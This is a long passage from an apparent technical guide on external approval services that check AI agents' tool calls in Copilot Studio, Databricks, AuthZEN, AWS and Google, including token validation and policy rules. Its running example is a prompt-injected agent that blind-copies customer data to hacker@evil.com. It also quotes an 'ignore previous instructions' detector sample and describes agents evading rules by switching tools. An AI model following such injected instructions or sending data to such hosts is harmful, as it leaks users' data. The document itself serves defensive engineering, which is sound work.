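The "to" address is the one the lookup returned, and the lookup fits what the user asked for. The "bcc" address appears nowhere else in the request, including the chat history. The agent's stated reason, that the user wants to notify the customer, doesn't explain the second recipient.

A service could catch this by comparing every address in inputValues with the addresses in the conversation and the earlier tool outputs. But this would miss many indirect prompt injections, because if the agent had read a document containing the attacker's instructions, the evil.com address would be in an earlier tool output and would match. The service also has to check which tool an address came from, since a customer database is a better source of recipients than a stranger's invoice.

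The service answers with a block:

```json
{
  "blockAction": true,
  "reasonCode": 112,
  "reason": "Noncompliant address in BCC field",
  "diagnostics": "{\"flaggedField\":\"bcc\"}"
}
```

Only blockAction is required. The service's developer chooses the reason codes, the reason is an explanation for people, and the diagnostics help with tracing and debugging. To allow the call, the service can return just blockAction set to false.

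The service returns a block with status 200 because it is a successful answer. Error statuses are for requests that the service couldn't process, such as one without a tool definition. A developer used to other web services might refuse a call with status 403, the code for "forbidden". Copilot Studio would treat that as an error and, by default, let the call run.

The lookup result is further evidence that Copilot Studio sends a request before each call, and not once for the whole plan as Microsoft's announcement describes. The request could contain the customer's address only if the lookup had already run. The blog post also describes a request before each action. The announcement may be a simplified description, or Microsoft may have changed the process after the preview began.

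### New fields and API versions

Each request's web address ends with a version, such as api-version=2025-05-01. Microsoft tells developers to accept unexpected fields and new values, and not to reject a request because its version is new. It considers all versions to date to be compatible with each other, but developers should still keep track of them.

This goes against the common security habit of rejecting any input that doesn't match a strict description. If Microsoft added one field and a strict service began rejecting requests, every rejection would count as an error, and under the default setting all the calls would run unchecked.

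Tolerating unfamiliar fields is also risky, because a service can ignore something important without anyone noticing. On Microsoft's page, the example request calls the earlier results previousToolOutputs, but the reference table calls them previousToolsOutputs, with an extra "s". A service written to expect one spelling would skip the other as an unfamiliar field and keep returning verdicts without the evidence that exposed the blind copy.

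The page has other inconsistencies. A tool's outputs are a single object in the example but a list in the reference table. Diagnostics is an object in the description of the answer but a string in the table and the examples, and a string is the safer choice. The lookup tool and the email tool in the example also share the ID tool-123, so a developer who reuses the example as test data could mistake one for the other.

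The service should accept both spellings and both shapes, and record the names of any fields it doesn't recognise. It also helps to capture a few real requests from a test agent before writing the detection rules, because they show what Copilot Studio actually sends.

### What happens after a block

Microsoft's documentation is inconsistent about whether an agent skips a blocked tool or stops altogether, but two other Microsoft pages suggest that stopping is likelier. The announcement describes the agent stopping and informing the user, and *Protect your environment in real-time during agent runtime* lists the same notice to the user among the effects of a Defender block.

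Stopping the agent is safer against an attacker, because an agent that only skips a tool still has the hostile instructions in its context and could try to send the same data through another tool. But stopping can leave work half done. The invoice agent in the Defender researchers' scenario records payment details in a customer database and then emails a confirmation. If the service blocks the email, the record may already exist, and a second attempt could create a duplicate.

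That agent also starts automatically, so there may be no user to read the notice. Its administrators would have to find the block in the agent's Activity History, where Microsoft says it appears with an error message stating that threat-detection controls intervened. Copilot Studio also keeps an audit log of every exchange with the outside service. When there is a user, Microsoft says only that the notice tells them their message is blocked. A service therefore shouldn't rely on the user seeing its reason, or any instructions in it such as "ask your manager to send this".

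#### Databricks

Databricks gives the caller more information, in a form that depends on what the policy blocked. When a policy blocks a request to a language model, the client receives status 200 and what looks like an ordinary assistant reply. The reply names the policy, and a separate object contains the reason in machine-readable form.

Databricks chose an ordinary reply to keep clients from triggering the same block on every later turn, since many of them, including coding agents, resend the entire conversation with each new message. After an error, the client would probably have no answer to add to the conversation, so the blocked message would still be unanswered in its next request.

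When a policy blocks a call to an MCP tool, Databricks returns a JSON-RPC error with the reason in its message. The agent can then explain the problem to the user or choose a permitted action. But a detailed reason could also help a manipulated agent find a version of the call that passes. Naming the rule that applied, but not the exact threshold or the list of forbidden values, would reduce that risk.

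Databricks' third verdict, ASK, has no equivalent in Copilot Studio. An example policy from Databricks returns ASK, with a message requesting confirmation, when an agent acting on a user's behalf tries to create an issue, push files or merge a code change. If the agent runs outside Databricks, the request reaches the user through an MCP feature that directs them to a web page. An approval service for Copilot Studio would have to block the same call and leave the user to make the change by hand.

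### AuthZEN

Because of these differences, a security vendor has to write a separate connection for each platform. Databricks requires outside vendors to implement Databricks' external policy interface, Google's gateway uses protocols from the Envoy proxy, and Copilot Studio uses the format described above. AuthZEN is an attempt by the OpenID Foundation to replace such formats with a single one. The foundation also developed OpenID Connect, a widely used standard for signing in to websites.

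AuthZEN's core is the Authorization API, which Gazitt, Brossard and Tulshibagwale (2026), in *Authorization API 1.0*, define as the messages between a policy enforcement point and a policy decision point. An approval service would be the decision point. A request has three required parts and one optional part:

- The subject is the user or program whose access is in question.
- The action is what they want to do.
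- The resource is the thing they want to do it to.
- The context, which is optional, can hold anything else about the circumstances, such as the time.

The email to evil.com could become the request below. The standard fixes the four top-level names and the type, id and name fields, but a developer would choose the rest.

```json
{
  "subject": { "type": "user", "id": "user-guid" },
  "action": { "name": "send_email" },
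  "resource": { "type": "recipient", "id": "hacker@evil.com" },
  "context": { "agent": "agent-guid" }
}
```

The answer contains a decision, true or false, and can include a context with reasons. In one of the standard's examples, the administrator gets the number of the policy that the request failed, while the user gets only a message about insufficient privileges. This separation would suit agents well, since the security team needs details that an attacker shouldn't have.

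AuthZEN and Copilot Studio both return a refusal with status 200, reserve error codes for faults, and require services to tolerate unknown fields. But a verdict of true blocks the action in Copilot Studio and allows it in AuthZEN. A program that translated between them without reversing the value would approve every detected attack and block everything else.

An AuthZEN request can also contain several checks. For an email with two recipients, the enforcement point could include a check for each and tell the service to stop at the first denial. A platform could send a whole plan this way only if it already had the inputs for every step. In the John Doe example it would not, because the recipient's address depends on the lookup.

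#### What the standard leaves open

Olivier, who co-chairs the working group, stresses that AuthZEN covers only the interface between enforcement and decision. It doesn't specify a policy language, where the service gets its information, or how the two sides authenticate.

AuthZEN's biggest gap for agents is in the context. A platform can include the conversation and earlier tool outputs there, but AuthZEN doesn't define fields for them. Two platforms could both comply while one sent the full chat history and the other sent none, so a service that judges whether a call fits the task would need separate code for each. AuthZEN is much better suited to permission checks, such as whether this user's agent may email this address. Those checks matter, but they wouldn't have caught the SharePoint attack in the Defender researchers' scenario, because every step was within the agent's permissions.

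#### Mapping tool calls

Another set of drafts, COAZ ("Compatible with OpenID AuthZEN"), describes how to turn a tool call into an AuthZEN request. In the February version, *AuthZen Profile for Model Context Protocol Tool Authorization* (Tulshibagwale and Olivier, 2026), each MCP tool publishes a mapping alongside its description. When an agent calls the tool, a gateway or the tool's server fills in the mapping from the call's inputs and the access token.

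In one example, a tool retrieves a customer's details. The subject is the user's identity, taken from the token, the action is the tool's name, and the resource is the customer number from the inputs. The context contains the agent's identity and the support case it is working on. A tool that copies a file requires two approval checks, one for reading the original and one for writing the copy.

The quality of the check depends on the mapping. If the mapping for an email tool includes the "to" field but omits the blind copy field, the request won't contain a blind-copied evil.com address, so the service can't take it into account. The tool's developer writes the mapping, so a company would need to review it before trusting the service's verdicts.

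*Getting Cozy with COAZ* (Tulshibagwale and Olivier, 2026) announced revised drafts in July that add a default mapping for every type of MCP message, so that a gateway can request decisions about tools whose developers wrote no mapping. A default can't specify which inputs of a particular tool are dangerous, so sensitive tools would still need their own mappings.

#### Approvals that take time

Another draft deals with actions that policy doesn't allow yet but could allow once someone approves them. In an example from the OpenID Foundation (2026), an agent tries to pay a vendor more than a set limit. The service refuses the payment but marks it as eligible for approval and specifies what approval requires. The agent keeps a reference to the pending request, a manager approves the request through the company's usual process, and the service evaluates the payment again before it goes ahead.

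This could help with agents that try to get around a refusal. Nick Davis, a vice president at the identity company Okta, says in the same announcement that agents work around policy boundaries in increasingly complex ways. Okta sells products in this area, and the announcement includes no data to support his claim, but an agent with a legitimate way to get permission would have less need to look for a workaround.

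#### Status and adoption

The Authorization API is finished. The OpenID Foundation's *Authorization API 1.0 Final Specification Approved* (2026) announced on 12 January that members had approved it by 81 votes to 1, with 25 abstentions. Later documents can add to version 1.0 but can't change it. COAZ and the approval profile, the parts written for agents, were still working drafts in the summer of 2026 and had yet to go through an intermediate version and a final vote.

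No major agent platform appears to use AuthZEN for its approval checks yet. Copilot Studio and Databricks require their own formats. AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) describes an engine that evaluates Cedar rules at Amazon's own gateway, so there is no outside service for a standard to connect. AuthZEN support is further along in general software. Foojay's *An Introduction to OpenID AuthZEN and authzen-enforcer, a Java SDK* (2026) uses Keycloak, an open-source identity server, as the decision point and presents a toolkit for querying it from Java programs.

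CrowdStrike might have reason to support a common format, since it sells products that connect to several agent platforms and employs Tulshibagwale, one of the working group's co-chairs. Platform owners have less to gain, because a proprietary format makes it harder for customers to move their security rules elsewhere.

A company that already runs an AuthZEN service for its other software can still use it with Copilot Studio by writing a small translator. The translator would receive each request at /analyze-tool-execution, send the AuthZEN service an equivalent request, reverse the answer and return it, all within Copilot Studio's one-second limit. A company with no approval service yet would do better to implement Microsoft's format directly or buy a product that already does.

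## Setting up trust between the platform and the service

Copilot Studio and an approval service usually communicate over the internet, so each needs proof of the other's identity. Without that proof, an outsider could send made-up tool calls and study the verdicts to find an attack the service would approve. An impostor service would be worse, because it would receive employees' conversations and could approve every call.

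The service proves its identity with a TLS certificate, just as a website proves to a browser that it controls its address. Copilot Studio proves its identity with a bearer token in each request. Microsoft Entra ID, the identity service that holds a company's directory of users and programs, issues the token, and most of the setup determines when it will do so.

### Copilot Studio's setup in order

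The company starts with its own tenant ID and the service's address, which the provider supplies. Microsoft recommends a PowerShell script that registers the application and adds the credential. Its dry-run option checks the values without creating anything. An administrator can do the same work by hand, as follows.

#### Registering the application

An application in Entra is a record that gives a program an identity. The company can create one without writing any software. The administrator chooses the single-tenant option, which limits the application to the company's own directory, and copies the application ID that Entra assigns.

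According to CrowdStrike, the application needs no permissions to use other Microsoft services. It's therefore best to register a new one. If the company reused an application that could already read mailboxes, the new credential could give Copilot Studio's connection that access too.

#### Adding the credential

A federated identity credential is a record telling an identity provider, here Entra, to accept a token from a named issuer and subject in place of a stored secret. The administrator selects "Other issuer" and "Explicit subject identifier", then enters two values:

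```
Issuer:   https://login.microsoftonline.com/{tenant ID}/v2.0
Subject:  /eid1/c/pub/t/{encoded tenant ID}/a/m1WPnYRZpEaQKq1Cceg--g/{encoded service address}
```

The issuer is the party that vouches for the token, in this case the company's own Entra tenant. The subject identifies the program that the token describes. Microsoft explains the subject's format in its instructions for Power Platform plug-ins, which use the same format. The code eid1 is the version of the format, c/pub stands for Microsoft's public cloud, and t introduces the tenant. Administrators must not change the part after "a". According to an answer in the forum thread *Blocker in Implementing SSO for Teams Bot* (2025), that part is the encoded ID of one of Microsoft's own applications, presumably Copilot Studio in this case.

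The credential also needs an audience, normally api://AzureADTokenExchange, which marks the incoming token as meant for this kind of exchange. The plug-in instructions list different audiences and subject prefixes for Microsoft's US government and Chinese clouds, so a company using one of those clouds should ask Microsoft which values Copilot Studio uses.

#### Getting the provider's authorisation

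The provider now has to accept the application. Zenity, a security vendor, asks the customer to enter the application ID and tenant ID in its portal, then adds the application to its allow list.

CrowdStrike also asks an administrator to approve its application in the customer's tenant so the application can take part in the token exchange. The approval screen labels the publisher as unverified, which CrowdStrike tells customers to expect. Attackers use similar screens to trick people into granting access, so the administrator should open the link from CrowdStrike's console, not from an email, and check that the application requests only permission to sign in and read the user's profile.

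A company that builds its own service must also register it in Entra. Microsoft requires the service to expose a scope (a named permission that other programs can request) equal to its base URL. For a service at https://security.contoso.com/api/threatdetection, the scope is https://security.contoso.com, without the path. The setup instructions, however, use "base URL" for the longer address, including the path. According to *Microsoft External Threat Detection*, the developer must also prove ownership of the domain by adding a value from Microsoft to the domain's DNS records, the public records that connect a domain name to its servers.

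#### Connecting the environment

In the Power Platform admin center, an administrator selects an environment, agrees to share data with the provider, and enters the application ID and the service's address. The address must match the one in the credential. Saving fails if the application is misconfigured or the provider hasn't authorised it.

The process may need three people. Microsoft says the person adding the credential must own the application or have an Entra role such as Application Administrator. The admin center requires the Power Platform Administrator role, and CrowdStrike's approval screen requires a Global Administrator or Privileged Role Administrator.

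### How the token exchange works

Microsoft's *Workload identity federation* describes the exchange for programs that run outside Microsoft's cloud, such as an automated job on GitHub. Applied to Copilot Studio, it would work like this:

1. Copilot Studio requests a token that identifies it.
2. The issuer signs a token containing the issuer and subject shown above, and returns it.
3. Copilot Studio sends this token to Entra with the company's application ID, and requests an access token for the approval service.
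4. Entra verifies the signature and compares the token's issuer, subject and audience with the credential on the application.
5. If they match exactly, Entra returns an access token.
6. Copilot Studio sends the access token to the approval service along with the proposed tool call.

The federated credential contains no secret, so an attacker who copies its issuer and subject still can't produce a token with a valid signature. The usual alternative is to create a password or certificate for the application and store a copy in the program that uses it. Someone could steal that copy, and an administrator has to replace it before it expires. If it expired first, tool calls would run unchecked by default.

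Someone could still steal the access token, which Microsoft sets by default to expire after a random period of 60 to 90 minutes. If Copilot Studio reuses a token during that time, the connection may keep working for more than an hour after an administrator deletes the credential. An administrator who needs to stop sharing data at once should turn off the connection in the admin center.

Copilot Studio also appears to be an exception to a rule that would otherwise rule out this setup. According to Microsoft's description, the exchange doesn't support tokens issued by Entra, but Copilot Studio's issuer is an Entra tenant. Microsoft documents at least one other exception. It accepts tokens from managed identities, which Azure provides for software running on it, if the identity and the application belong to the same tenant. A forum user, sanderaernouts (2025), in *AADSTS700236*, reported an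 error after trying a similar exchange across two tenants. The company should therefore register the application in the tenant where its agents run.

### Encoding the tenant ID and address

The subject contains the tenant ID and the service's address in Base64, a way of writing bytes as letters, digits and a few symbols. A tenant ID is 16 bytes long, written as 32 hexadecimal digits in five groups. Microsoft's encoding commands use a function from its .NET programming framework that reverses the bytes within each of the first three groups, while many other tools keep the bytes in written order.

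For the tenant 12345678-1234-1234-1234-123456789012, the two methods give different results:

| Byte order | Bytes | Encoded tenant ID |
|---|---|---|
| .NET | 78563412 3412 3412 1234 123456789012 | eFY0EjQSNBISNBI0VniQEg |
| As written | 12345678 1234 1234 1234 123456789012 | EjRWeBI0EjQSNBI0VniQEg |

Only the .NET version will match. Both versions are 22 characters long, so they can't be told apart by length. A 48-character result means someone encoded the ID as text, hyphens included. In Python, the correct byte order comes from the UUID's `bytes_le` attribute, not `bytes`.

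Microsoft's documentation makes this error easy to miss. The encoding commands use the sample tenant ID 11111111-2222-3333-4444-555555555555, which encodes the same way in either byte order because the bytes within each group are identical. A developer could test a faulty script against that example and get the expected answer. The plug-in instructions cover converting the ID to hexadecimal and then to Base64, but not byte order.

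The final encoded values must also use "-" instead of "+" and "_" instead of "/", and omit any "=" signs at the end. Without the "/" replacement, they could add extra slashes to the subject.

The address is ordinary text, so byte order doesn't matter, but every character does. With Microsoft's sample address, https://provider.example.com/threat_detection/copilot, the complete subject is:

```
/eid1/c/pub/t/eFY0EjQSNBISNBI0VniQEg/a/m1WPnYRZpEaQKq1Cceg--g/aHR0cHM6Ly9wcm92aWRlci5leGFtcGxlLmNvbS90aHJlYXRfZGV0ZWN0aW9uL2NvcGlsb3Q
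```

A slash at the end of the address would change the last characters of its encoded form from b3Q to b3Qv, so the subject would no longer match. Some vendors do part of this work for customers. Palo Alto Networks' *Configure SaaS Agent Security as an External Threat Detection System* tells customers to copy the address in both plain and encoded form, and CrowdStrike's console computes the whole subject.

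*Microsoft External Threat Detection* encodes an address ending in /analyze-tool-execution, whereas Microsoft specifies the address without that ending. The blogger reports that the setup worked, but Microsoft's version is safer to follow.

### What binding the credential to one address achieves

Because the subject includes the service's address, the credential works only for connections to that address. Suppose an attacker takes over a Power Platform administrator's account and replaces the address with their own. Copilot Studio would request a token with the new address in the subject, Entra would find no matching credential, and the save would fail. The attacker would also need to control an Entra application to redirect the company's conversations.

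This protection is weaker if the same account can register applications, because the attacker could then create a new application with a credential for their own address and enter its ID in the admin center. Keeping the two administrator roles separate helps, as does an alert whenever someone adds a credential. An application can have up to 20 credentials, and each is another way to obtain tokens in the application's name.

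The binding also makes it harder to switch to a different service address. Zenity has separate addresses for Europe and the United States, and credentials can't contain wildcards, so a customer moving between the two needs a second credential. The customer should add it before changing the address in the admin center.

A web address can also change owners. A Microsoft notice from 2026 recommends replacing GitHub credentials that rely on the names of repositories and their owners, because someone could reuse an old name and gain the access it had. Copilot Studio's credential has a similar weakness. If a provider let its domain lapse, a new owner could get a valid certificate for it, and the credential would still match. A company that changes provider should therefore turn off the old connection and delete its credential.

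### Checking the incoming token

The service should check the token before it examines the tool call. An access token consists of a header, a set of named values called claims, and a signature. The service needs to check the following:

- Signature: Entra signs the token with a private key and publishes the matching public key. The header identifies which key to use. Entra changes its keys from time to time, and Microsoft suggests checking for new ones every 24 hours.
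- Issuer (iss): this must match the expected Entra tenant exactly.
- Audience (aud): this must identify the approval service. According to Microsoft, it's always the service's application ID in version 2.0 tokens, but it can be the service's URL in version 1.0 tokens.
- Expiry (exp): the service must reject a token after this time. A separate claim, nbf, gives the earliest time at which the token is valid.
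- Tenant (tid): this must belong to a company that uses the service.
- Application ID (appid in version 1.0, azp in version 2.0): this must be the application that the provider authorised for that tenant.

Microsoft's *Secure applications and APIs by validating claims* warns that a service that checks the tenant but not the application could admit every program with an identity in that tenant. The same guidance says that a service that authorises callers by application ID should also check the idtyp claim to confirm that Entra issued the token to the application itself. This check matters because a token that an application obtained on behalf of a user can sometimes reach other parties.

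Entra's signature covers the token but not the request body, so a provider with many customers should use the tenant ID in the token to choose which company's rules apply. If the provider used the ID in the body instead, one customer could insert another's tenant ID and test attacks against that company's rules.

The sample code in *Microsoft External Threat Detection* reads the tenant and application IDs from the token without verifying its signature, so anyone could send a forged token with any IDs. It also writes the whole token to a log, where someone could copy it. The post says that it leaves out validation, but a developer who starts from this code still has to add all the checks, preferably with an established library such as Microsoft.Identity.Web.

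A service that never downloads Entra's new keys will eventually reject genuine requests, which Copilot Studio treats as errors.

### Common setup errors

Entra saves a credential with the wrong subject without warning. The mistake appears only when a token exchange fails, which for Copilot Studio normally happens when the administrator selects Save in the admin center. The error message is vague, but "Copy error info" gives the details.

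| Error | Cause | What to check |
|---|---|---|
| AADSTS700016 | Entra can't find the application | The application ID, and whether the application is in the right tenant |
| AADSTS70025 | The application has no federated identity credential | Whether someone added the credential to another application |
| AADSTS7002111 | No credential has the right issuer | The tenant ID, the /v2.0 ending and any stray spaces |
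| AADSTS7002137 | No credential has the right subject | Byte order, a slash at the end of the address, spaces and invisible characters |
| The application ID doesn't match the one registered for webhook access | Microsoft Defender, as the provider, hasn't authorised the application | The application's status with Defender |

If the last error appears, Entra has already issued a token, so there is no need to change the credential.

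When the subject is wrong, Microsoft advises copying the expected value from the error message, but the administrator should first decode the address in it. In Microsoft's sample error, the encoded address ends in beKAiw, which decodes to the end of "contoso.provider.com" followed by a zero-width space, an invisible character that people can pick up when they copy text from a web page. The character probably came from the address in the admin center, so retyping that address is a better fix than copying the expected subject, which would make the two values match but leave the character in place. Decoding would also reveal a misspelled or malicious address before anyone creates a credential for it.

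### Google Cloud and AWS

Google's Agent Gateway can't confirm the identity of a custom approval service. Google Cloud says the gateway encrypts the connection but doesn't validate the service's certificate. The encryption protects the traffic from eavesdroppers, but the gateway would also connect to an impostor. Anyone who could redirect the service's name to their own server could read the agents' tool calls and approve them.

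Google therefore recommends keeping the service inside the company's Virtual Private Cloud (VPC), its private network within Google Cloud. A vendor's service on the public internet doesn't follow this recommendation. If the vendor can't supply software to run inside the network, the company could run a small relay there that validates the vendor's certificate and forwards each request, which adds some delay.

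Google's sample configuration for a custom service also gives the gateway no credential to present. Unless the company adds another way for the gateway to prove its identity, the service should accept connections only from the gateway. For Model Armor, Google's own filter, an administrator instead gives the gateway's service account, an identity for software, access to the filter.

AWS avoids most of this because its interceptor runs as a Lambda function inside AWS. AWS's *Permissions for interceptors* requires the gateway's service role, the identity under which the gateway acts, to have the lambda:InvokeFunction permission. AWS enforces the permission, so the interceptor's developer doesn't have to write token checks for the gateway. It's sensible to grant the permission only for the interceptor's function. If that function consults an approval service outside AWS, the company has to set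 up authentication for that connection itself.

The remaining choice is whether the interceptor should receive request headers. AWS's *Configuration* describes a setting, passRequestHeaders, that is off by default. When it's on, the interceptor receives every header, including any bearer tokens. The token may be the only way to identify the user behind a call, but the interceptor then holds a credential that could work elsewhere, and careless logging could expose it. The page warns about this, but developers who copy its sample commands will turn the setting on. An interceptor that consults an outside service should send the user's ID but not the token.

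### What authentication leaves unproven

A valid token proves which application sent a request, and a valid certificate proves that the service controls its address. Neither is evidence that the verdict is sound. The request to approve the email with evil.com in the blind-copy field would arrive with a valid token, since the company's own agent proposed the email. A compromised service, or one with poor rules, would answer from the correct address with a valid certificate.

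Authentication also doesn't prove that the approved call is the one that runs. In Copilot Studio's documented format, the service's answer has no signature and no copy of the inputs it approved. If a fault changed an email's recipient after approval, the service's records would show only the original address. A company can look for such changes by comparing those records with the mail server's log of recipients. To prevent them, the service would have to sign a fingerprint of the approved inputs, and the email tool would have to refuse any call that didn't match it.

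## How the service reaches its verdict

An approval service has four main ways to decide whether a tool call may run, and it can combine them. It can apply fixed rules to the tool, the user and the input values. It can run a detector trained to recognise prompt injection, or ask a language model whether the call fits the user's request. It can also apply rules to the whole sequence of the agent's actions, for example to block an email that would normally be allowed because the agent has already read confidential data. The methods need different information and make different mistakes, and some are too slow for Copilot Studio's one-second limit.

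### Fixed rules

A fixed rule compares a field of the request with a value or a list. Companies can write such rules in a policy language, such as Cedar, which AWS runs at its own gateway, or Rego, the language of the open-source Open Policy Agent (OPA). AI SDK's *Policy-Based Tool Approvals*, part of the documentation for a toolkit for building agents, explains how to check each tool call against a Rego policy. A company called Contoso could use the same format to forbid blind copies to outsiders:

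```rego
package agent.call

default decision := {"decision": "allow"}

decision := {"decision": "deny", "reason": "outside address in BCC"} if {
  input.tool.name == "send_email"
  input.args.bcc != ""
  not endswith(input.args.bcc, "@contoso.com")
}
```

The deny rule applies only when all three of its conditions are true, as they are for an email blind-copied to hacker@evil.com. An email without a blind copy, or a call to any other tool, gets the default verdict, which is allow. AI SDK's examples omit the `if` keyword, which OPA has required since version 1.0.

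A rule like this is fast, gives the same answer to the same call every time, and doesn't change its verdict because of hidden instructions. Its mistakes come from cases its author didn't foresee. If the blind-copy field contained "hacker@evil.com; ann@contoso.com", the email would go out because the text ends in the right domain. The rule also ignores the "to" and "cc" fields. Contoso could instead let agents write only to listed addresses, but that would block the first email to every new customer.

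An agent can also get around a rule by using another tool. For example, a rule against publishing code with the git tool doesn't stop an agent from running the same git command through a general command-line tool. AI SDK suggests that the check on the command-line tool should extract the underlying command, apply the same rule to it, and deny any command it can't interpret. It recommends fixed rules for questions a program can settle by comparing fields, such as permissions and spending limits, but advises against relying on such rules to judge meaning.

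#### Searching for known attack patterns

Some services search all the text in a call instead of checking named fields. *AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) describes one that extracts text from inputs nested up to 32 levels deep, so an attacker can't easily hide a command there. It compares the text with 22 patterns in seven categories, such as destructive database commands and paths to password files, and then applies the company's own rules.

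AEGIS blocked all 48 attacks in the researchers' tests, but they took the attacks from documented techniques, which such patterns are written to match. They acknowledge that AEGIS may miss new variants. It also blocked six of 500 legitimate calls (1.2%), all of them database queries that used "OR" to combine conditions, which one of the patterns flags as a sign of attack. An agent that mostly queries databases could therefore have a much higher rate of false blocks.

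#### Duties and exceptions

A company may want to attach a duty to an action it allows. *Deontic Policies for Runtime Governance of Agentic AI Systems* (Joshi, Finin and colleagues, 2026) points out that Rego and Cedar have no built-in way to do this. The paper's prototype, AgenticRei, uses a policy language that covers duties and exemptions as well as permissions and prohibitions.

In one example, a payments agent may not make a high-value payment on its own. Approval from a treasury authority named in the policy overrides the ban. The approved payment creates a duty to file a report with the US agency that combats financial crime, unless the other party belongs to an exempt class. Cedar can't rank the permission above the ban, because a Cedar rule that forbids something always overrides one that permits it. The policy's author would have to write the exception into the ban itself.

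AgenticRei can also reason about categories. A ban on reading health information covers every type of record the company's data model places in that category, including types added later. With a plain list, a new type stays unprotected until someone updates the rule.

Joshi and colleagues support their case with worked examples and preliminary timings, but they didn't test how many attacks AgenticRei stops or how many legitimate calls it blocks. The prototype only simulates the credential check. It can record a duty and raise an alarm after a missed deadline, but the agent still has to carry out the duty. In Copilot Studio, the documented response from the service has no field for instructions to the agent, so the service would have to send the notification or file the report itself.

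### Trained detectors

A trained detector is a model that has learned to tell prompt injection from ordinary text by training on examples of both. It gives each piece of text a score, and the service blocks the call if the score exceeds a threshold. Lowering the threshold catches more attacks but also blocks more legitimate calls.

Pangea's sample log entry from AIDR, CrowdStrike's detection product, shows a user asking a human resources chatbot to ignore its previous instructions and retrieve the full record for a social security number. The detector for malicious prompts returns a confidence of 1, the maximum, and AIDR blocks the request. The detector can find the phrase about ignoring instructions only if the service passes on the user's message.

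Detectors assess the text rather than the agent's action, so a security training document that quotes an attack could set one off even if the agent is only summarising it. They also miss failures that happen without an attacker, because there is no hostile text to detect. Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Sapien*, cite as an example a web-browsing agent that couldn't find what it was looking for, collected the site owner's contact details and sent unsolicited emails. Detectors also do worse against attackers who adapt to them than against a fixed set of known attacks.

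Tiffany and colleagues expect small classifiers to answer in tens of milliseconds, while the largest language models take seconds. The classifiers would therefore answer well within Copilot Studio's time limit.

### A language model as judge

The service can use a language model to compare the proposed call with what the user asked for. The model receives the request, the call, any relevant context and the company's policy, and outputs whether the call should run. It could identify a salary search as unrelated to a request about an invoice, even if nobody had written a rule about salaries.

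The service's mistakes often come from missing context. It might, for example, approve the deletion of an old test account because nothing in its input shows that a nightly payment run depends on the account. In Claude Code's auto mode, a classifier reviews the agent's actions so the user doesn't have to approve each one. Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* warns that the classifier may allow a risky action if the user's intent is ambiguous or if the classifier lacks context about the user's environment. It may also block harmless actions. Text that the service reads can manipulate its verdict too.

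The judge's accuracy depends heavily on its instructions. Ravindran and Deochake (2026), in *ToolGuardian*, gave an openly available model, gpt-oss-120b, prepared facts about 20 scenarios in which an agent uses tools. With a full written policy, the model judged all 20 correctly. Without the explicit rules and the list of dangerous combinations, it judged 15 correctly, wrongly blocked four, and allowed one unsafe workflow. The test was small, but it suggests that a company should give a judge its actual policy and not just ask whether a call seems safe.

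Large models may also be too slow. In experiments by Tiffany and colleagues, language model checks added 1.4 to 3.5 seconds per task on one test suite, depending on the model. Tasks averaged only 0.6 such checks, so a typical check took roughly two seconds or more. At that speed, Copilot Studio would time out before the verdict arrived, so a company that wants to use a language model as a judge there needs a smaller and faster one.

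Sapien, a research system, limits what it asks the judge. For example, it might give the judge only an email and a document, and ask whether the email faithfully summarises the document. Fixed rules still determine who may receive the email, so an attacker who fools the judge can change the email's content but can't redirect it. Narrow questions can also cause errors. One judge rejected an update to a rent "standing order" because the system had stored the order as a one-time payment.

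### Rules over the sequence of actions

Some violations can't be found in any single call. Suppose a purchasing agent reads a confidential contract with one supplier and then emails a competing supplier. The approval request for the first call contains a contract number and the name of a tool the agent uses every day. The request for the second contains a known supplier's address and a polite message about prices. The agent has permission for both calls, and only the combination suggests a leak. *Runtime Governance for AI Agents* (Kaptein, Khan and Podstavnychy, 2026) uses a similar example, a database read followed by an external email, to argue that rules should cover the agent's whole sequence of actions.

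A simple version of the service needs to store very little. When it approves a read from a confidential source, it marks the conversation. If the agent later proposes an email to an outside address, the service finds the mark and blocks the email. The typical error is a false block, because the mark records what the agent has read but not what the email contains. The service would block even a harmless note about a delivery date if the agent had opened a confidential contract earlier in the conversation.

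In Copilot Studio, the service has to keep this record itself. The platform sends the results of earlier tools, but Pangea describes these as results from the current plan. If the user asks about the contract in one message and asks for the email in the next, the platform's second request to the service may not include the contract. The service can use the conversation ID to connect the two requests.

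#### Scoring the risk

Kaptein and colleagues propose a more general form, in which each policy is a function that gives the proposed action a score:

```
π(A, P, s*, Σ) → a number from 0 to 1
```

- A is the agent's identity, including its registered purpose.
- P is the path so far, meaning every completed step with its inputs and outputs.
- s* is the action the agent proposes.
- Σ is a record shared across all the company's agents.

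Ordinary access control uses only the agent's identity and the type of action. A rule against leaks must also take into account the path, meaning the steps the agent has taken so far. In one example, each tool result has a sensitivity level, and the score for an outside message is the highest level the agent has read so far divided by the top of the scale. After the agent reads something at level 4 out of 5, any outside email scores 0.8, while an internal email scores 0.

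The shared record can help the service catch violations that involve several agents. For example, a bank may have to keep its advisory staff's knowledge of pending deals from its traders. If an advisory agent reads deal data and then delegates a task to a trading agent, it could pass on that knowledge even if each agent is acting within its own permissions. A service that checks each agent separately would miss the violation.

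To combine several policies, the service calculates the probability that the action violates at least one:

```
v = 1 − (1 − π₁)(1 − π₂) … (1 − πₙ)
```

Five policies that each score 0.2 give a combined score of 1 − 0.8⁵, or about 0.67, so the service could block an action that scores low on every policy. The formula is correct only if the policies are independent. If two policies react to the same outside email, the formula would count the same concern twice.

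The paper is a proposal with no experiments. Kaptein and Khan acknowledge that the scores in current software indicate severity rather than measured probability. They work at Kyvvu, whose policy engine connects to Copilot Studio, so they have a commercial interest in the approach.

#### Evidence from ToolGuardian

Ravindran and Deochake tested the effect of adding rules about combinations of calls in 20 scenarios, 12 with a single call and eight with several steps. In one case study, an agent reads database records and then updates a GitHub project. Both tools are legitimate, but ToolGuardian blocks the update because the records would flow to an outside service.

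Researchers compared formal logic rules, ordinary program code and a language model, and all three judged every scenario correctly. When the researchers removed the rules about combinations of calls from the program code, it still judged all 12 single calls correctly but allowed four unsafe workflows. This supports including such rules, but the researchers designed the scenarios alongside the rules and worked from prepared facts instead of running live agents. The perfect scores therefore don't show how well the rules would work in a company.

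Sequence rules also depend on knowing which tools read sensitive data and which send it elsewhere. A tool's description may not reveal this, so ToolGuardian examines tools before a company admits them. Its test used eight harmless tools and eight malicious variants with unchanged descriptions. Using the descriptions, records of system activity and trial runs, all three methods rejected six of the malicious tools and none of the harmless ones. However, the logic rules restricted all eight harmless tools.

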